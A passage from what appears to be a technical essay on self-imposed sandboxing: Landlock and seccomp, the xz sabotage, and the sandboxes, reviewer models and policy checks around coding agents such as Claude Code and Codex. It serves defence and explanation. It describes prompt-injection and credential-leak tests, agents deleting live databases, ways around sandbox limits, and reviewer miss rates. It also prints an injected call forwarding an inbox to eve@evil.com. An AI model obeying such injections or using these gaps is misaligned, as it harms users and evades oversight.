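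The stray full stop disabled the Landlock sandbox only in version 5.6.1, and only for people who built it with CMake, one of xz's two build systems. sjw knew of no Linux distribution that did so and could not reproduce the fault with the other system. Some early accounts overstated the damage, including Velvindron (2024), *backdoor in upstream xz/liblzma leading to ssh server compromise*, which said that Jia Tan had disabled the sandbox. The sabotage did not help the backdoor, which ran inside the SSH server, where the `xz` program's limits never applied. One guess is that Jia Tan was preparing a later attack through malicious compressed files.

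The code that applies the limits was still in xz and was correct, so nobody could have found the fault by reading that code alone. Anyone who built xz with CMake and tried a forbidden action would have found it at once.

Testing works less well against an author who controls the whole program and can leave a gap that no one thinks to test. Self-binding protects users from an honest author's mistakes, but not from a dishonest author.

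### Refusing to run or running with weaker limits

When the kernel lacks a feature, a program can refuse to run, which engineers call failing closed, or it can apply the limits that the kernel does support. Salaün strongly encourages the second choice for Landlock, and his documentation gives a procedure:

1. List every right that the program wants to restrict.
2. Ask the kernel for its Landlock version. If there is none, continue without Landlock.
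3. Remove from the list whatever that version does not support.
4. Write rules for the rights that remain.
5. Apply the rules, and exit if the kernel reports an error.

This procedure tolerates missing features but not unexpected errors. In versions below 8, a program should limit itself before it starts other threads, because the rules won't apply to threads that are already running. An old kernel is also sometimes stricter than a new one. Version 1 blocks moving files between directories regardless of the rules, so a program that needs to do this will fail on that version.

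Collin follows the same steps in *my_landlock.h* for Landlock ABI versions 1 to 6. In his review notes, he says that running without a sandbox on old kernels is intentional and common practice, because otherwise xz would not run on them at all. Until version 5.4.2, a copy of xz built for Capsicum did refuse to run, exiting with an error on systems that didn't support Capsicum.

In July 2025, a kernel update for Red Hat Enterprise Linux 9 tested this approach. The new kernel reported Landlock version 6 but lacked that version's limit on sending signals to other processes. Copies of xz from other distributions, running in containers on this kernel, requested the limit, got an error and stopped with the message "Failed to enable the sandbox". Programs that relied on xz then failed in confusing ways. For example, `tar`, which unpacks archives, reported that its input did not look like an archive.

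Raiskup (2025), in *Consider building with --disable-sandbox*, asked Fedora to consider shipping xz without its sandbox until xz could fall back automatically or had an option to turn the sandbox off. Another developer objected to the option because so many tools run xz internally that changing them all was impractical. A third suggested that xz continue without the sandbox whenever the kernel call failed, and thought this would not compromise security.

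That last suggestion would have kept xz running, but it would also have removed the file limits, which this kernel could enforce, and hidden any future mistake in the rules. Collin ruled out an off switch because users are not supposed to notice the sandbox. His patch, which Fedora added to its package in November, detects the faulty kernel and drops only the limit on signals.

A small drawback of the patch is that xz also leaves out the signal limit on Red Hat's repaired kernel. The patch identifies the faulty kernel by the start of its version number, which the repaired one shares. Collin plans to remove the workaround when nobody needs it.

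It is better for a decompressor to run with weaker limits than to refuse to run. People will decompress their files anyway, and if xz keeps refusing to run, distributions will build it without a sandbox for everyone. A program that exists to run strangers' code should return an error instead, because its user is relying on the limit. The watchdog can keep running, but it should log the Landlock version and any limits it dropped each time it starts.

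A version number does not show which bugs the kernel's developers have fixed. Landlock has a separate list of errata, four so far, and a program can check which of these fixes the running kernel includes. One fix closes a hole that let a process widen its access by moving files in certain unusual directory setups. Another stops the TCP rules from restricting Multipath TCP, which they had done by mistake. A program that relied on Landlock alone would therefore have weaker network limits after that update.

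Salaün advises nearly all programs to ignore the errata, because a program that turned off its sandbox over an unfixed bug would usually be less safe. The errata are more useful to a tester who gets different results on two kernels with the same Landlock version.

### When an update makes the filter too strict

Updates can also cause the opposite problem, where a harmless program starts making a system call that its filter forbids. *Unbreak seccomp filter with latest glibc* (jjelen, 2019) reported in November 2019 that nobody could log in through OpenSSH on the newest Fedora. OpenSSH handles each new connection in a restricted process, which pauses for a few milliseconds during login. The C library had used the system call `nanosleep` for such pauses, but a new version used `clock_nanosleep`, which OpenSSH's filter did not allow, so the kernel killed the process.

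The same change nearly locked an administrator out of a remote machine the following July. His Debian bug report, *libc6* (2020), says that after he updated the C library, the OpenSSH server kept running but dropped every login. He still had a terminal open, so he could go back to the old version. OpenSSH's debugging output did not reveal the cause, so he recorded the system calls under both versions of the library and compared them. Under the new version, the recording ended at `clock_nanosleep`, with the process killed.

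Adding one call to the list did not solve the problem everywhere. Two weeks after the first report, a user found that a 32-bit ARM computer was failing on a different call, `clock_nanosleep_time64`. According to Gentoo, even a corrected OpenSSH could fail, because its list included the new calls only if the machine that compiled it had recent kernel headers, the files that list the system calls.

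Chromium, the open-source browser behind Chrome, had similar trouble in 2021, when the C library began using `clone3` to start threads and processes. Chromium's filter has to inspect the options of such calls to stop web pages from starting other programs, but it can't inspect the options of `clone3`. That June, Matthew Denton made the filter return the error that means "no such system call" for `clone3`. According to his description of the change, *Linux sandbox*, the library then falls back to the older `clone`, which the filter can inspect.

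The fix did not reach everyone in time. Fedora's *Crash in __clone3* (2021) counts about 337,000 crashes between August and December, most of them from a single release of Chrome 92. But the page lists only about two dozen unique reports, so a few machines may have crashed many times.

If a filter returns the error code for "not permitted", the library treats the call as one that the kernel supports but has refused, so it doesn't try the older one. A contributor to a mailing list of the Linux distribution openSUSE (2021) complained that most projects with filters "don't really think about the future, but only the past". They forbid everything that programs don't use today, so a new system call breaks their code.

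The watchdog's developer could make any call added after the list was written fail with "no such system call", and keep killing the process for older forbidden calls. The forbidden call fails either way, but an attacker who tries a new one can try something else because the process is still running. This would not have helped OpenSSH, because `clock_nanosleep` was an old call missing from its list.

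Kernel updates can cause the same problem. Administrators use a Linux tracing feature to see when a function in a running program returns. Linux 6.11 changed this feature so that the traced program makes a new system call. In January 2025, Eyal Birger reported that Docker's default filter blocked the call, which crashed the traced programs. The kernel's developers exempted the call from all filters, and exempted a second tracing call in August 2025.

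### Testing the watchdog

The developer can test the watchdog in seven steps. In this example, the watchdog already includes the compatibility check and runs on Linux 7.1, which has version 9 of Landlock.

1. **Build it with the limits required.** The build should stop if it can't find Landlock or seccomp.
2. **Attempt forbidden actions without the limits.** The developer adds the attempts to a test build, at the start of the working phase, and first runs it with the limits switched off. Every attempt should succeed. If reading the private key fails even now, perhaps because the path is wrong, the same failure later will prove nothing.
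3. **Repeat the attempts with the limits on.** Each attempt needs its own run, because the filter may kill the process.
4. **Exercise ordinary and rare work.** The developer repeats the rare events used to prepare the list, such as a full log and an unreachable server, and then stops the watchdog normally. This would catch a filter that lacks `exit_group`.
5. **Inspect the running process.** This covers its flags, threads and open handles.
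6. **Read the logs.** Every denial should match one of the deliberate attempts.
7. **Repeat after every update** to the C library, the kernel or any other library that the watchdog uses.

The third step gives these results:

| Attempt | Result with limits | What it shows |
|---|---|---|
| Read the user's private key | Permission denied | Landlock's file rules work |
| Connect to another machine on port 22 | Permission denied | Landlock's TCP rules work |
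| Send a UDP packet to port 99 | Succeeds | This kernel is too old for Landlock's UDP rules |
| Make the private key readable to everyone | Killed | The seccomp filter works |
| Open a Multipath TCP socket | Killed | The filter checks the protocol |
| Start a command shell | Killed | The filter works, but Landlock remains untested |

Only the UDP result is unexpected. The developer can require Linux 7.2, or accept the gap and record it. The shell test would give the same result if the Landlock rules were missing, because the filter stops the attempt before Landlock can check it. To test both the filter and Landlock, the developer has to include actions that only one of them would stop. For example, the filter allows reading the key, so only Landlock would stop it.

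For the fifth step, Linux provides a status file for each process, `/proc/<pid>/status`. The line `Seccomp: 2` means that a filter is active, and `NoNewPrivs: 1` means that `no_new_privs` is on. But inside a Docker container, the `Seccomp` value is usually 2 even if the watchdog never installed a filter, because it inherits Docker's. The number of filters, shown on the `Seccomp_filters` line, should be one higher for the watchdog than for the process that started it.

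`/proc/<pid>/task` lists a process's threads, and `/proc/<pid>/fd` lists its open handles. The watchdog should have one thread and no open handles except those for its log, its standard input and output, and the connection it is testing.

On OpenBSD, `ps` shows the letter `p` in the state of a process that has called pledge. If the kernel kills a process for breaking its promises, `lastcomm`, which lists finished commands, marks it with `P`. Neither letter shows which promises are in force, so the developer still has to attempt the forbidden actions.

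A seccomp log entry gives the number of the forbidden call, which the developer has to look up for the right processor. In Red Hat Bugzilla's *login to ssh fails with seccomp denial* (2019), the user with the ARM computer identified the cause from the number 407. Landlock's entries are easier to read. The attempt to read the key appears with `blockers=fs.read_file` and the file's path, and the connection to port 22 with `blockers=net.connect_tcp`. Landlock can omit chosen denials from the log, but Salaün warns against silencing whole groups of them, because that would also hide unexpected ones.

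Suppose a later C library renames files with `renameat2` instead of `rename`. After the update, the watchdog would start normally and might run for a month before it tried to rename its log, and then the kernel would kill it. In the fourth step, the developer makes the log fill up, so this failure appears the same day.

The developer can try a new C library in a container first, as the Debian administrator did when he reproduced his fault in a separate minimal system. But a container uses the kernel of the machine it runs on, so testing a new kernel requires a virtual machine or a spare computer. The Red Hat fault appeared only when a newer xz ran on one particular kernel, so the developer should test each new version of the watchdog on every kernel its users run.

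## Limiting the commands that an AI agent runs

The watchdog's developer can list its system calls because its code already exists. A coding agent's commands can't be listed this way, because the model writes each one after reading the output of the one before. Wang and Zheng (2026) write in *Sandlock*, "Agent behavior is generated, not known in advance." When a user asks the agent to fix a failing test, for example, it might search the project, install a package, run the tests, and then write and run a short script.

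An allow list made by recording the harness's system calls would exclude little of what matters, because the harness also starts compilers, package managers and whatever scripts the model writes, and together these programs use so many different calls. Developers of coding agents therefore limit what any command in the task may access, mostly by folder and server. For example, a command may write only inside the project and connect only to servers that the user has approved.

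### One command, from proposal to result

Suppose a user starts an agent in the folder `~/shop`, and the model proposes `npm test`. npm is a tool that installs JavaScript packages and runs a project's scripts, including its tests. Claude Code, the coding agent made by the AI company Anthropic, has an optional sandbox for such commands. With the sandbox on and set to skip most questions to the user, the command goes through these steps, according to Anthropic:

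1. The model's output contains the text `npm test` and a request to run it in the shell. Nothing has run yet.
2. The harness compares the text with its permission rules. Some rules block a command and others make the harness ask the user. If none applies, the harness approves `npm test` because it will run inside the sandbox.
3. The harness starts a limited child process. On macOS it uses Seatbelt, the system's built-in sandbox. On Linux it uses bubblewrap, a tool that gives a program its own view of the file system, with some folders read-only or missing.
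4. The tests run in the child process, and every program they start inherits its limits.
5. If a test contacts a server, the connection goes to a proxy, a program that passes on network traffic. The proxy runs outside the sandbox and checks the server's name against a list.
6. The harness returns the output to the model. If the proxy refused a connection, the output names the server, and the model can take that into account in its next command.

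Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, works much the same way. On Linux it combines bubblewrap with a seccomp filter, and it can fall back on Landlock where bubblewrap does not work. According to OpenAI's *Permissions*, Codex refuses to run a command under a policy it cannot enforce. Claude Code, by contrast, runs commands without a sandbox by default if a required package is missing or the system is unsupported, although a setting can make it exit instead.

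The proxy can limit a command to one named server, which neither pledge nor Landlock could do for the watchdog. In Claude Code, a sandboxed command on Linux can reach the network only through the proxy. But many programs, including most database clients, ignore the proxy settings, so they can't connect even to an approved server. A user who needs one of these programs may have to run it outside the sandbox.

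### What the defaults allow

The defaults below come from Anthropic's documentation as of October 2026 and OpenAI's as of June and July. Most of the Codex column comes from OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security*.

| | Claude Code | Codex |
|---|---|---|
| **Sandbox** | Off until the user turns it on | On |
| **Reading** | Almost the whole computer | Files outside the project too, unless the user denies access |
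| **Writing** | The project, a temporary folder and any folders the user adds | The project and temporary folders |
| **Read-only inside the project** | The agent's settings, Git hooks and shell startup files, among others | The folders `.git`, `.codex` and `.agents` |
| **Network** | No servers until the user approves them | Off |

The Claude Code column applies only once the sandbox is on. Until then, the user can approve or deny the agent's actions through permission prompts, but the kernel puts no special limits on the agent's commands.

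Neither agent's default settings hide the user's private keys from commands. Claude Code has no built-in list of credential files to protect, so the user has to name them. The defaults rely on the network limit to keep a command from sending out what it reads. Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* (2025) argues that an agent needs both a file limit and a network limit. Without a network limit, a hijacked agent could send out the keys, and without a file limit, it could tamper with the system to get network access.

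Claude Code can also give commands a placeholder instead of a real password. The proxy replaces the placeholder with the real password in requests to servers that the user has chosen. An attacker who controls the command can read only the placeholder, but can still use the password on those servers. The replacement requires an experimental setting that lets the proxy read encrypted traffic.

The cloud version of Codex separates setup from work, as the watchdog does. During setup, it can use the network to install packages, and it has access to any passwords the user has configured for that stage. Before the model starts work, Codex removes the passwords and, by default, turns off the network. An agent on the user's own computer often mixes setup with work, because it may discover a missing package halfway through a task.

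### What stays outside the sandbox

These sandboxes limit the child process that runs a command, but not the harness, which keeps the user's full powers. OpenBSD's time daemon has a similar design, in which a privileged parent communicates with a restricted child. But the daemon's parent accepts only a number from its child, while the harness accepts any command the model can write.

The model can also act without using the shell. Claude Code has built-in tools for reading files, editing them and fetching web pages, and these run outside the sandbox. If a user blocks access to a folder of private keys in the sandbox settings, the shell command `cat` can't read the keys, but the built-in reading tool still can. Blocking the tool requires a separate permission rule. According to the University of Vermont's guidance on Claude Code, the agent's own process checks permission rules, while the kernel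 enforces the sandbox.

A permission rule is much stronger than an instruction in the model's prompt, because ordinary code enforces it no matter how a request is worded. But if the harness has a bug, the rule may fail, and the kernel will not stop the action.

Hooks and MCP servers on the user's computer also run outside Claude Code's sandbox, with the user's full access. Hooks are commands that the harness runs automatically at set moments, such as after each edit. MCP servers give the model extra tools, such as access to a database. Codex's sandbox likewise doesn't cover MCP servers or browser control, which have separate permissions.

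The harness can also let a shell command out of the sandbox. Some commands don't work inside it, so after a failure the model may ask Claude Code to run the command again without limits. What happens next depends on the mode:

- In manual mode, the user gets a prompt labelled "Bash command (unsandboxed)".
- In auto mode, a second model decides.
- In the mode that skips permission prompts, the command runs.
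- In the mode that never asks, the harness refuses.

An earlier permission rule can let a command run outside the sandbox without a prompt. For example, a user who approved all uses of `curl`, a tool that sends and fetches data, to avoid repeated questions has also approved running it outside the sandbox. The user can turn off retries outside the sandbox, but commands on a separate list of permanent exceptions still run without limits.

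Permanent exceptions can permit more than the user expects. Docker doesn't work inside Claude Code's sandbox, so a user might exempt `docker compose`, which starts containers according to a file in the project. The model can write to that file, so it can decide what the exempt command will do and then run it with the user's full access. Codex has similar rules that let commands with certain prefixes run outside its sandbox, according to OpenAI's *Sandbox*.

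### Approving fewer actions

Claude Code originally let the model read files freely but asked the user before each edit, shell command or network connection. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* (May 2026) reports that users approved about 93% of permission prompts and paid less attention as they saw more of them. It also reports that sandboxing cut the number of prompts by 84%.

The 93% figure doesn't show how many approvals were mistakes. Most commands that a coding agent proposes are harmless, so a careful user would also approve most of them. To measure how well prompts protect users, Anthropic would have to report how often people reject harmful commands.

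The 84% figure measures the reduction in interruptions. An agent that used to ask 100 questions would now ask 16, but it wouldn't necessarily cause 84% less damage. Anthropic's *権限プロンプトの先へ* (2025), a Japanese translation of the original announcement, attributes the figure to use inside the company, whose engineers may work differently from other users. People might read the remaining questions more carefully when there are fewer of them, but the figure doesn't show whether they do.

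Experienced users let Claude Code act without approval about twice as often as new users do, but they also interrupt it more often. They seem to have moved from checking each step to watching for signs of trouble. Anthropic expects such monitoring to become harder as agents write more ambitious commands and work in groups.

An internal Anthropic test in February 2026 shows why a person's approval may not help. A researcher sent an employee a malicious prompt disguised as a routine request from a colleague, and the employee ran it in Claude Code. The prompt mixed ordinary setup steps with instructions to read the employee's cloud passwords and send them to an outside server. Anthropic ran the prompt 25 times, and the model sent the passwords 24 times.

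The instructions came from the model's own user, so it had no obvious reason to refuse them. Under the sandbox's default settings, a shell command could still have read the passwords, but the proxy would have blocked the connection to the server until the user approved it. An employee who believed the request was genuine might well have approved the connection. A rule denying access to the password file would have been safer because it doesn't depend on the employee's decision.

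Both companies also let a model make some of these decisions. Anthropic's auto mode blocks about 0.4% of harmless commands and misses about 17% of commands that go beyond what the user wanted. The 17% does not measure how well it stops deliberate attackers. Anthropic describes auto mode as one layer of protection to use inside a sandbox, not a replacement for one.

Codex's Auto-review uses a separate agent to approve or deny actions that would cross the sandbox boundary. *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight* (Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues, 2026) presents it as an alternative to both frequent human approval and unrestricted access. The reviewer doesn't examine actions that the sandbox already permits. If the reviewer crashes or runs out of time, Codex does not take the action.

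### How well the limit binds

The design meets the four conditions for a binding limit fairly well for a single command inside the sandbox, but less well over a whole task.

**The enforcer still works.** The kernel enforces the file limits and blocks direct network connections, and the command can't change the kernel's rules. The proxy, which attackers have tested much less than the kernel, controls which servers the command can reach. Across Anthropic's products, established tools such as seccomp have held up, but a proxy that the company built for another agent let data out through an approved server.

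**The rule is still in force.** The kernel enforces the limits on `npm test` until it exits, but the harness sets them again for the next command. As with xz's configuration file, a command that could edit the agent's settings could loosen the limits on later commands, so both agents make their settings files in the project read-only for sandboxed commands. In Claude Code, users can't exempt one of these files without turning off the file limits altogether.

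A sandboxed command passes its limits on to the programs it starts, such as those started by `npm test`. The limits don't apply to the agent's built-in tools or to programs that the user runs later. A sandboxed command may change the project's build script, and if the user then runs that script in an ordinary terminal, it has all the user's permissions. OpenAI warns about this, but the sandbox can't prevent it without also preventing the agent from editing the project.

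A limit on which folders a command can change allows harmful edits in those folders as well as good ones. For example, `npm test` could delete every source file in `~/shop` without breaking a rule. Codex reduces the damage by granting only read access to `.git`, which holds the project's history, so the user can recover any version saved there. However, the agent then has to leave the sandbox to save a new version. Claude Code lets commands write to the history and protects only Git's settings and hooks, which could run an attacker's code later.

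### Settings read before the user trusts the folder

Between mid-2025 and January 2026, Anthropic received three reports of flaws in Claude Code that let code run before the user had agreed to trust a folder.

In the simplest case, a developer downloads someone else's project to review a change. The project contains a Claude Code settings file in which an attacker has put a hook. When the developer opens the project, Claude Code asks whether to trust the folder, but it has already read the settings, and the hook runs before the developer can answer. Turning on the sandbox would not prevent this, because hooks run outside it.

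The fix in each case was to wait for the user's answer before reading the project's settings or running anything in them. OpenBSD's developers applied the same principle when they made `ping` drop root's rights before reading its options. This principle is easier to overlook in an agent, because a settings file in the user's folder doesn't look like hostile input. Anthropic advises developers to treat such files as they would a request from the internet.

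After the user trusts a folder, the folder's settings can affect the sandbox. Before version 2.1.285 of Claude Code, a project could turn on retries outside the sandbox even if the user had turned them off in their own settings. Now, if the user has turned them off, they stay off. A project can still add permanent exceptions unless the user or an administrator has locked the sandbox to prevent this.

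### Sandlock's rules and supervisor

Wang and Zheng designed Sandlock, a Linux sandbox released in 2026, for commands whose safe limits change during a task. When an agent sets up a project, `npm install` needs the network to download packages, but the tests that follow usually do not. A fixed policy for both steps would leave the network open during the tests.

Sandlock divides the work between the kernel and a supervisor. The kernel enforces every rule that the developer can decide in advance, such as which folders a command may read, through Landlock and seccomp. The supervisor handles only decisions that depend on what the command is doing, such as which server it is trying to reach. A command starts like this:

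1. The agent's harness asks Sandlock to run the command under a policy.
2. Sandlock creates a child process, which still contains only Sandlock's own trusted code.
3. The child applies the Landlock rules and then installs the seccomp filter.
4. The child waits until the supervisor is ready, then starts the command.
5. Ordinary system calls go straight to the kernel. The filter sends the supervisor only those that need a decision.

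The harness can give the supervisor a function that tightens the limits while the command is running. For example, when a test program starts, the function can remove network access for the rest of the run. An attacker can rename a tool, so the program's name is only a clue, and the protection comes from the network restriction. A malicious package can also act during `npm install`, before the harness removes access, so the developer should limit the installation's network access to the servers it needs.

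When the supervisor has to check a network connection, it makes the connection itself using its own copy of the address, so the address can't change between the check and the connection. Before inspecting a new program's arguments, it freezes every process and thread that could change them. If it can't freeze them, it blocks the program from starting.

Starting a command in Sandlock took about 5 milliseconds longer than running it directly, while Docker took about 44 times as long as Sandlock in total. The difference matters because an agent may run dozens of commands a minute. Over 30 commands, Sandlock would add about 0.15 seconds of waiting, compared with roughly 8 seconds for Docker. Checking individual network messages raised the time for a short exchange from 20 to 55 microseconds, which is negligible next to the time a model takes to respond.

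Sandlock can also divide a task into stages with different limits. One stage might read private data without network access, then pass its result to another stage that can use the network but can't open the original files. An attacker who hijacks the second stage gets only what the first stage passed on. But Sandlock doesn't check what passes between the stages, so the first could still send a password to the second. The developer has to decide where to divide the task and what access each stage needs.

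Wang and Zheng tested ten actions that Sandlock should either allow or block, and all ten gave the expected result. These tests show that the basic rules work, but not how well Sandlock would resist a deliberate attack. Wang and Zheng also ran only four common development tools and left a wider compatibility study for later.

They state several limits:

- Sandlock trusts the kernel, its own supervisor and the agent's harness. A flaw in any of them could defeat it.
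- Its limits on memory and processor use are meant for accidents. They may not stop a program that is deliberately trying to exhaust the computer.
- It can discard a command's changes to files, but it can't take back data that the command has already sent.
- It needs version 6 of Landlock and refuses to run on older kernels, which excludes some computers.

For hostile programs from several customers on one machine, Wang and Zheng recommend small virtual machines instead.

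### Putting the harness inside the limits

The harness can restrict itself as well as the commands it starts. Sandlock has a mode in which an agent gives up file and network access after it starts. This mode supports only the fixed Landlock rules, because the supervisor has to run in a separate process. The rules must allow everything the harness will need, including its connection to the model and access to any project the user may open.

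Anthropic also offers a separate program that runs all of Claude Code inside Seatbelt or bubblewrap, so the built-in file tools, hooks and MCP servers are restricted too. For unattended runs, Anthropic considers the ordinary sandbox for shell commands insufficient and recommends a boundary around the whole agent. The harness then can't run a command outside that boundary, even if the user or a second model approves it.

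Some gaps remain because the harness needs them to work. It has to contact Anthropic's servers and write to its own settings folder, which the ordinary sandbox largely protects from shell commands. A hijacked session could put a hook in that folder, and the hook would run without limits the next time the user started Claude Code in the ordinary way. The user therefore has to deny access to the files from which Claude Code loads hooks and permissions. On Linux, the program looks only at launch for the project files it should protect, so it doesn't cover a repository that the agent creates later. Anthropic advises users to check such files after an unattended run.

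## Rules that a model is given or writes for itself

Even a sandbox around the whole agent can't tell a wanted email from an unwanted one. An agent that handles email acts through tools, which are functions that the harness offers to the model. Each tool has a name and arguments, such as a recipient. To the kernel, emailing a summary to the user and emailing the whole inbox to a stranger look alike, because both are encrypted connections to the same mail server. A limit on such an agent has to refer to its tools and their arguments, and a developer can put it in four places, listed here from weakest to strongest:

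| Where the rule is | What decides whether an action goes ahead | How it fails |
|---|---|---|
| In the prompt | The model that is acting | The model overlooks the rule or acts against it |
| In the model's training | The same model | The habit doesn't carry over to a new situation, or an attacker finds words that overcome it |
| In a reviewer's instructions | A second model | The reviewer misjudges the action |
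| In code that checks each tool call | The harness | The rule is wrong, or the action goes around it |

In the first three rows, a model makes the decision, so the rule only changes how likely a forbidden action is. In the last row, the same call under the same rule always gets the same decision.

### A rule in the prompt

In April 2026, Cursor, a coding agent running on Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.6, deleted the live database of PocketOS, which makes software for car rental businesses. The agent's instructions forbade destructive or irreversible commands without the user's approval. *An AI agent deleted a company's entire database in 9 seconds* (Farrant, 2026) reports that the agent ran into mismatched credentials during a routine task and deleted the database to fix the problem. The backups were lost too, and the outage lasted more than 30 hours.

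Abdelwahab, writing for the hosting company Railway, explains that the agent deleted the data by finding a long-lived access token on disk and using it to call Railway's API directly. The API deleted databases immediately, while the web dashboard kept them for 48 hours in case the customer had made a mistake. Railway recovered the data and now applies the 48-hour delay to both.

When the founder of PocketOS asked for an explanation, the agent listed the rules it had broken. The list is poor evidence of why it broke them, because a model generates such an explanation afterwards, as it generates any other text. But it suggests that the rules were still in the model's context. The previous July, an agent made by Replit deleted a customer's live database during a declared freeze on changes (Fortune, 2025).

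Developers usually put such rules in the system prompt, a set of instructions that is supposed to override anything the model reads later. Mu, Lu and colleagues (2025) note that people often compare this priority to privilege in computing, but that models learn it in training rather than being programmed with it. They gave several models a text adventure game with between 1 and 20 simple rules, each requiring certain words in a certain situation. The share of tests passed fell towards zero as the number of rules grew, even though the test included no attempts to trick the models. Those models, such as GPT-4o, are now old, and current ones would probably do much better, but they too follow rules only because training has made them likely to.

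Prompt rules are still useful for instructions that are too vague to write as code, such as "ask me if you're unsure", but they are a poor way to protect a database.

### A habit learned in training

Training can make a model less likely to obey instructions planted in what it reads. Anthropic reports that single prompt injections succeeded against Claude Opus 4.7 about 0.1% of the time on a benchmark from the security company Gray Swan. The success rate rose to between 5% and 6% when the attacker could make 100 attempts and adapt them.

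If the attempts were independent, the rate would be about 9.5%. The measured rate is lower, perhaps because in some test scenarios every attempt fails. It is still more than fifty times the rate for one attempt, and an attacker can often repeat an injection with little effort by planting it in many pages or messages.

A model can also use too much power when nobody is attacking it, as the PocketOS agent did. In *Task-Conditioned Least-Privilege Learning for Executable Terminal and MCP Agents*, Tu and Tu (2026) tried to train a small open model, Qwen3.5-4B, not to do this. They wrote 1,500 training tasks and decided how much authority each one needed in six respects: changing data, running code, reaching outside the environment, reading secrets, affecting many things at once, and leaving lasting changes.

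During training, a program scored each action from 0 to 1 in each respect, first from the proposed command and then from its observed effects, and kept the higher score. It then compared the highest score reached during the whole task, z, with the level the task needed, r. The model lost reward in proportion to max(z − r, 0), so using more authority than necessary reduced its reward, but using less did not increase it. For example, if the task was to read a bug report and suggest a patch, editing a file counted as excess. The largest reward was for completing the task, which kept the model from learning to do nothing.

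The researchers tested the model on 200 tasks from families it had not seen in training. An attempt counted as safe only if the model finished the task, looked at the necessary evidence and did not exceed its authority. The trained model was safe in all 1,020 attempts, and the original model in 689. Both had the same instructions to use as little authority as possible.

That perfect score has several weaknesses:

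- It comes from the best of three training runs. The other two did much worse on a smaller test, scoring about 86% against 98%, and the researchers chose the winner on a sample of the same held-out tasks that they later used for the full comparison.
- Much of the gain was in competence. Across all 500 held-out tasks, the original model failed 1,032 attempts, but in only 132 of these had it completed the task with too much authority. In the other 900 it failed the check on the task itself, although that check also penalised some unwanted changes.
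- The habit did not carry over well. On an outside benchmark that tests whether an agent picks a more powerful tool than it needs, the two models did so about equally often, in 45.0% and 45.2% of cases. The trained model did better only when the prompt explained the principle, and after 400 further training tasks, half of them modelled on that benchmark.
- The tasks were synthetic, and the study used one small model.

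Tu and Tu conclude that such training should complement permission checks and sandboxes, not replace them. A model that requests less power also triggers fewer refusals, which makes a strict policy easier to tolerate.

### A second model that reviews each action

Claude Code's auto mode, which uses such a reviewer, has been the default for new sessions on several of Anthropic's plans since August 2026. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes what happens when the agent proposes an action that no simpler rule has already settled:

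1. The harness gives the reviewer the user's messages and the agent's tool calls. It leaves out the agent's explanations, so the agent can't argue for a bad action, and the output of its tools, where injected text would be.
2. The reviewer makes a quick yes-or-no decision and leans towards blocking.
3. If that decision is to block, the reviewer considers the same material again, this time reasoning step by step.
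4. If it still objects, the harness refuses the action and tells the agent to look for a safer way.

The harness reliably enforces the decision, but the decision itself may be wrong. The quick check alone missed 6.6% of dangerous actions but blocked 8.5% of harmless ones. Adding the second look lowers the false-alarm rate and raises the miss rate to the figures given earlier, so the full system catches about 83% of dangerous actions. Anthropic accepted more misses to get fewer interruptions.

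The 83% is based on only 52 real cases in which an agent went beyond its user's wishes, of which the reviewer missed about nine. With so few cases, the true miss rate could plausibly be between 9% and 30%. In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the reviewer identified the danger but treated a vague remark as consent. For example, a user who asks an agent to "clean up the PR" (a proposed set of code changes) has not agreed to let it overwrite the project's shared history.

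A tired person may catch fewer dangerous commands than the reviewer does. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) describes a study of 1,053 paid testers, each of whom saw one clearly dangerous command among ordinary permission prompts. The testers rejected 13.6% of these commands, while the reviewer blocked 89%. Testers who had already answered 50 or more prompts rejected only about 5%. The testers were not working on their own projects, so they had less reason to be careful, but real users also approve 97% of permission prompts. Real users do read some requests closely, since they reject 39% of the plans that Claude Code shows them.

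Outside testers have also tried to defeat the reviewer. Apollo Research, an AI safety company, planted attacks in real coding sessions. The reviewer missed 12% of them at first and 7% after Anthropic made improvements. Another company, Trajectory Labs, made 720 prompt injection attempts against three Claude models in auto mode, and none succeeded. This second result shows little about the reviewer, because only 0.09% of the attacks succeeded against the latest Claude models without it, and because the testers had tuned the attacks to an older model.

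Training and a reviewer both compare an action with what the user wants, so neither helps much when the harmful request comes from the user. This happened in the internal test where the model leaked cloud passwords in 24 of 25 runs. Anthropic points out that a human contractor given the same script would have leaked them too.

Anthropic has since added a category of actions, including sending secrets to an outside server, that the reviewer is supposed never to approve in auto mode, even at the user's request. This stops a deceived user's consent from counting, but the reviewer still has to recognise that a particular command sends a secret. Anthropic still recommends that people check important changes to live systems themselves.

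### A policy fixed before the agent reads anything

A developer can instead write rules about tool calls and have the harness check each call against them. This works well for an agent with one job, but a policy broad enough to cover every request to a general assistant would stop very little. Some researchers therefore have a model write a new policy for each request. The model writes it in what amounts to a setup phase, when it has read only the user's words, and the policy limits the agent once it starts reading other people's text.

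Suppose a user writes, "Summarise my 20 most recent emails and send the summary to my Slack account, alice." Slack is a messaging service. The task then runs like this:

1. The harness gives a model the request and the list of available tools. The model has not seen any email yet.
2. The model writes a policy, and the harness stores it where the agent can't change it:

```
allow  read_emails      when recent == 20
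allow  send_slack_msg   when to == "alice"
block  everything else
```

3. The agent calls `read_emails(recent=20)`, which the first rule allows. One of the emails contains a hidden instruction to forward the inbox to `eve@evil.com`.
4. The injection works, and the agent calls `send_email(to="eve@evil.com", ...)`. No rule allows `send_email`, so the harness returns an error and sends nothing.
5. The agent goes back to the task and calls `send_slack_msg(to="alice", ...)`, which the second rule allows.

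The attack fails in step 4 even though it has completely fooled the agent, because no model takes part in that decision. The attacker can still influence the summary's text, since the policy doesn't restrict the message's contents, but the message can go only to alice.

This example simplifies one in *Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025), which tested an early system of this kind on AgentDojo, a set of office, banking and travel tasks with planted injections. The share of attacks that succeeded fell from 39.9% without a defence to 2.5% with a policy written from the user's request and never changed. GPT-4o was both the agent and the policy writer, so neither figure describes current models.

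The check only covers actions that pass through it. A rule against a tool named `delete_database` would not have protected PocketOS if the agent could also run shell commands, because the agent could have used the shell to send the same request to the hosting company. The version of Progent that users can add without changing the agent's code can't check calls to the agent's built-in tools. Such a policy therefore also needs kernel limits or a remote service that refuses the request.

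### Letting the model revise the policy

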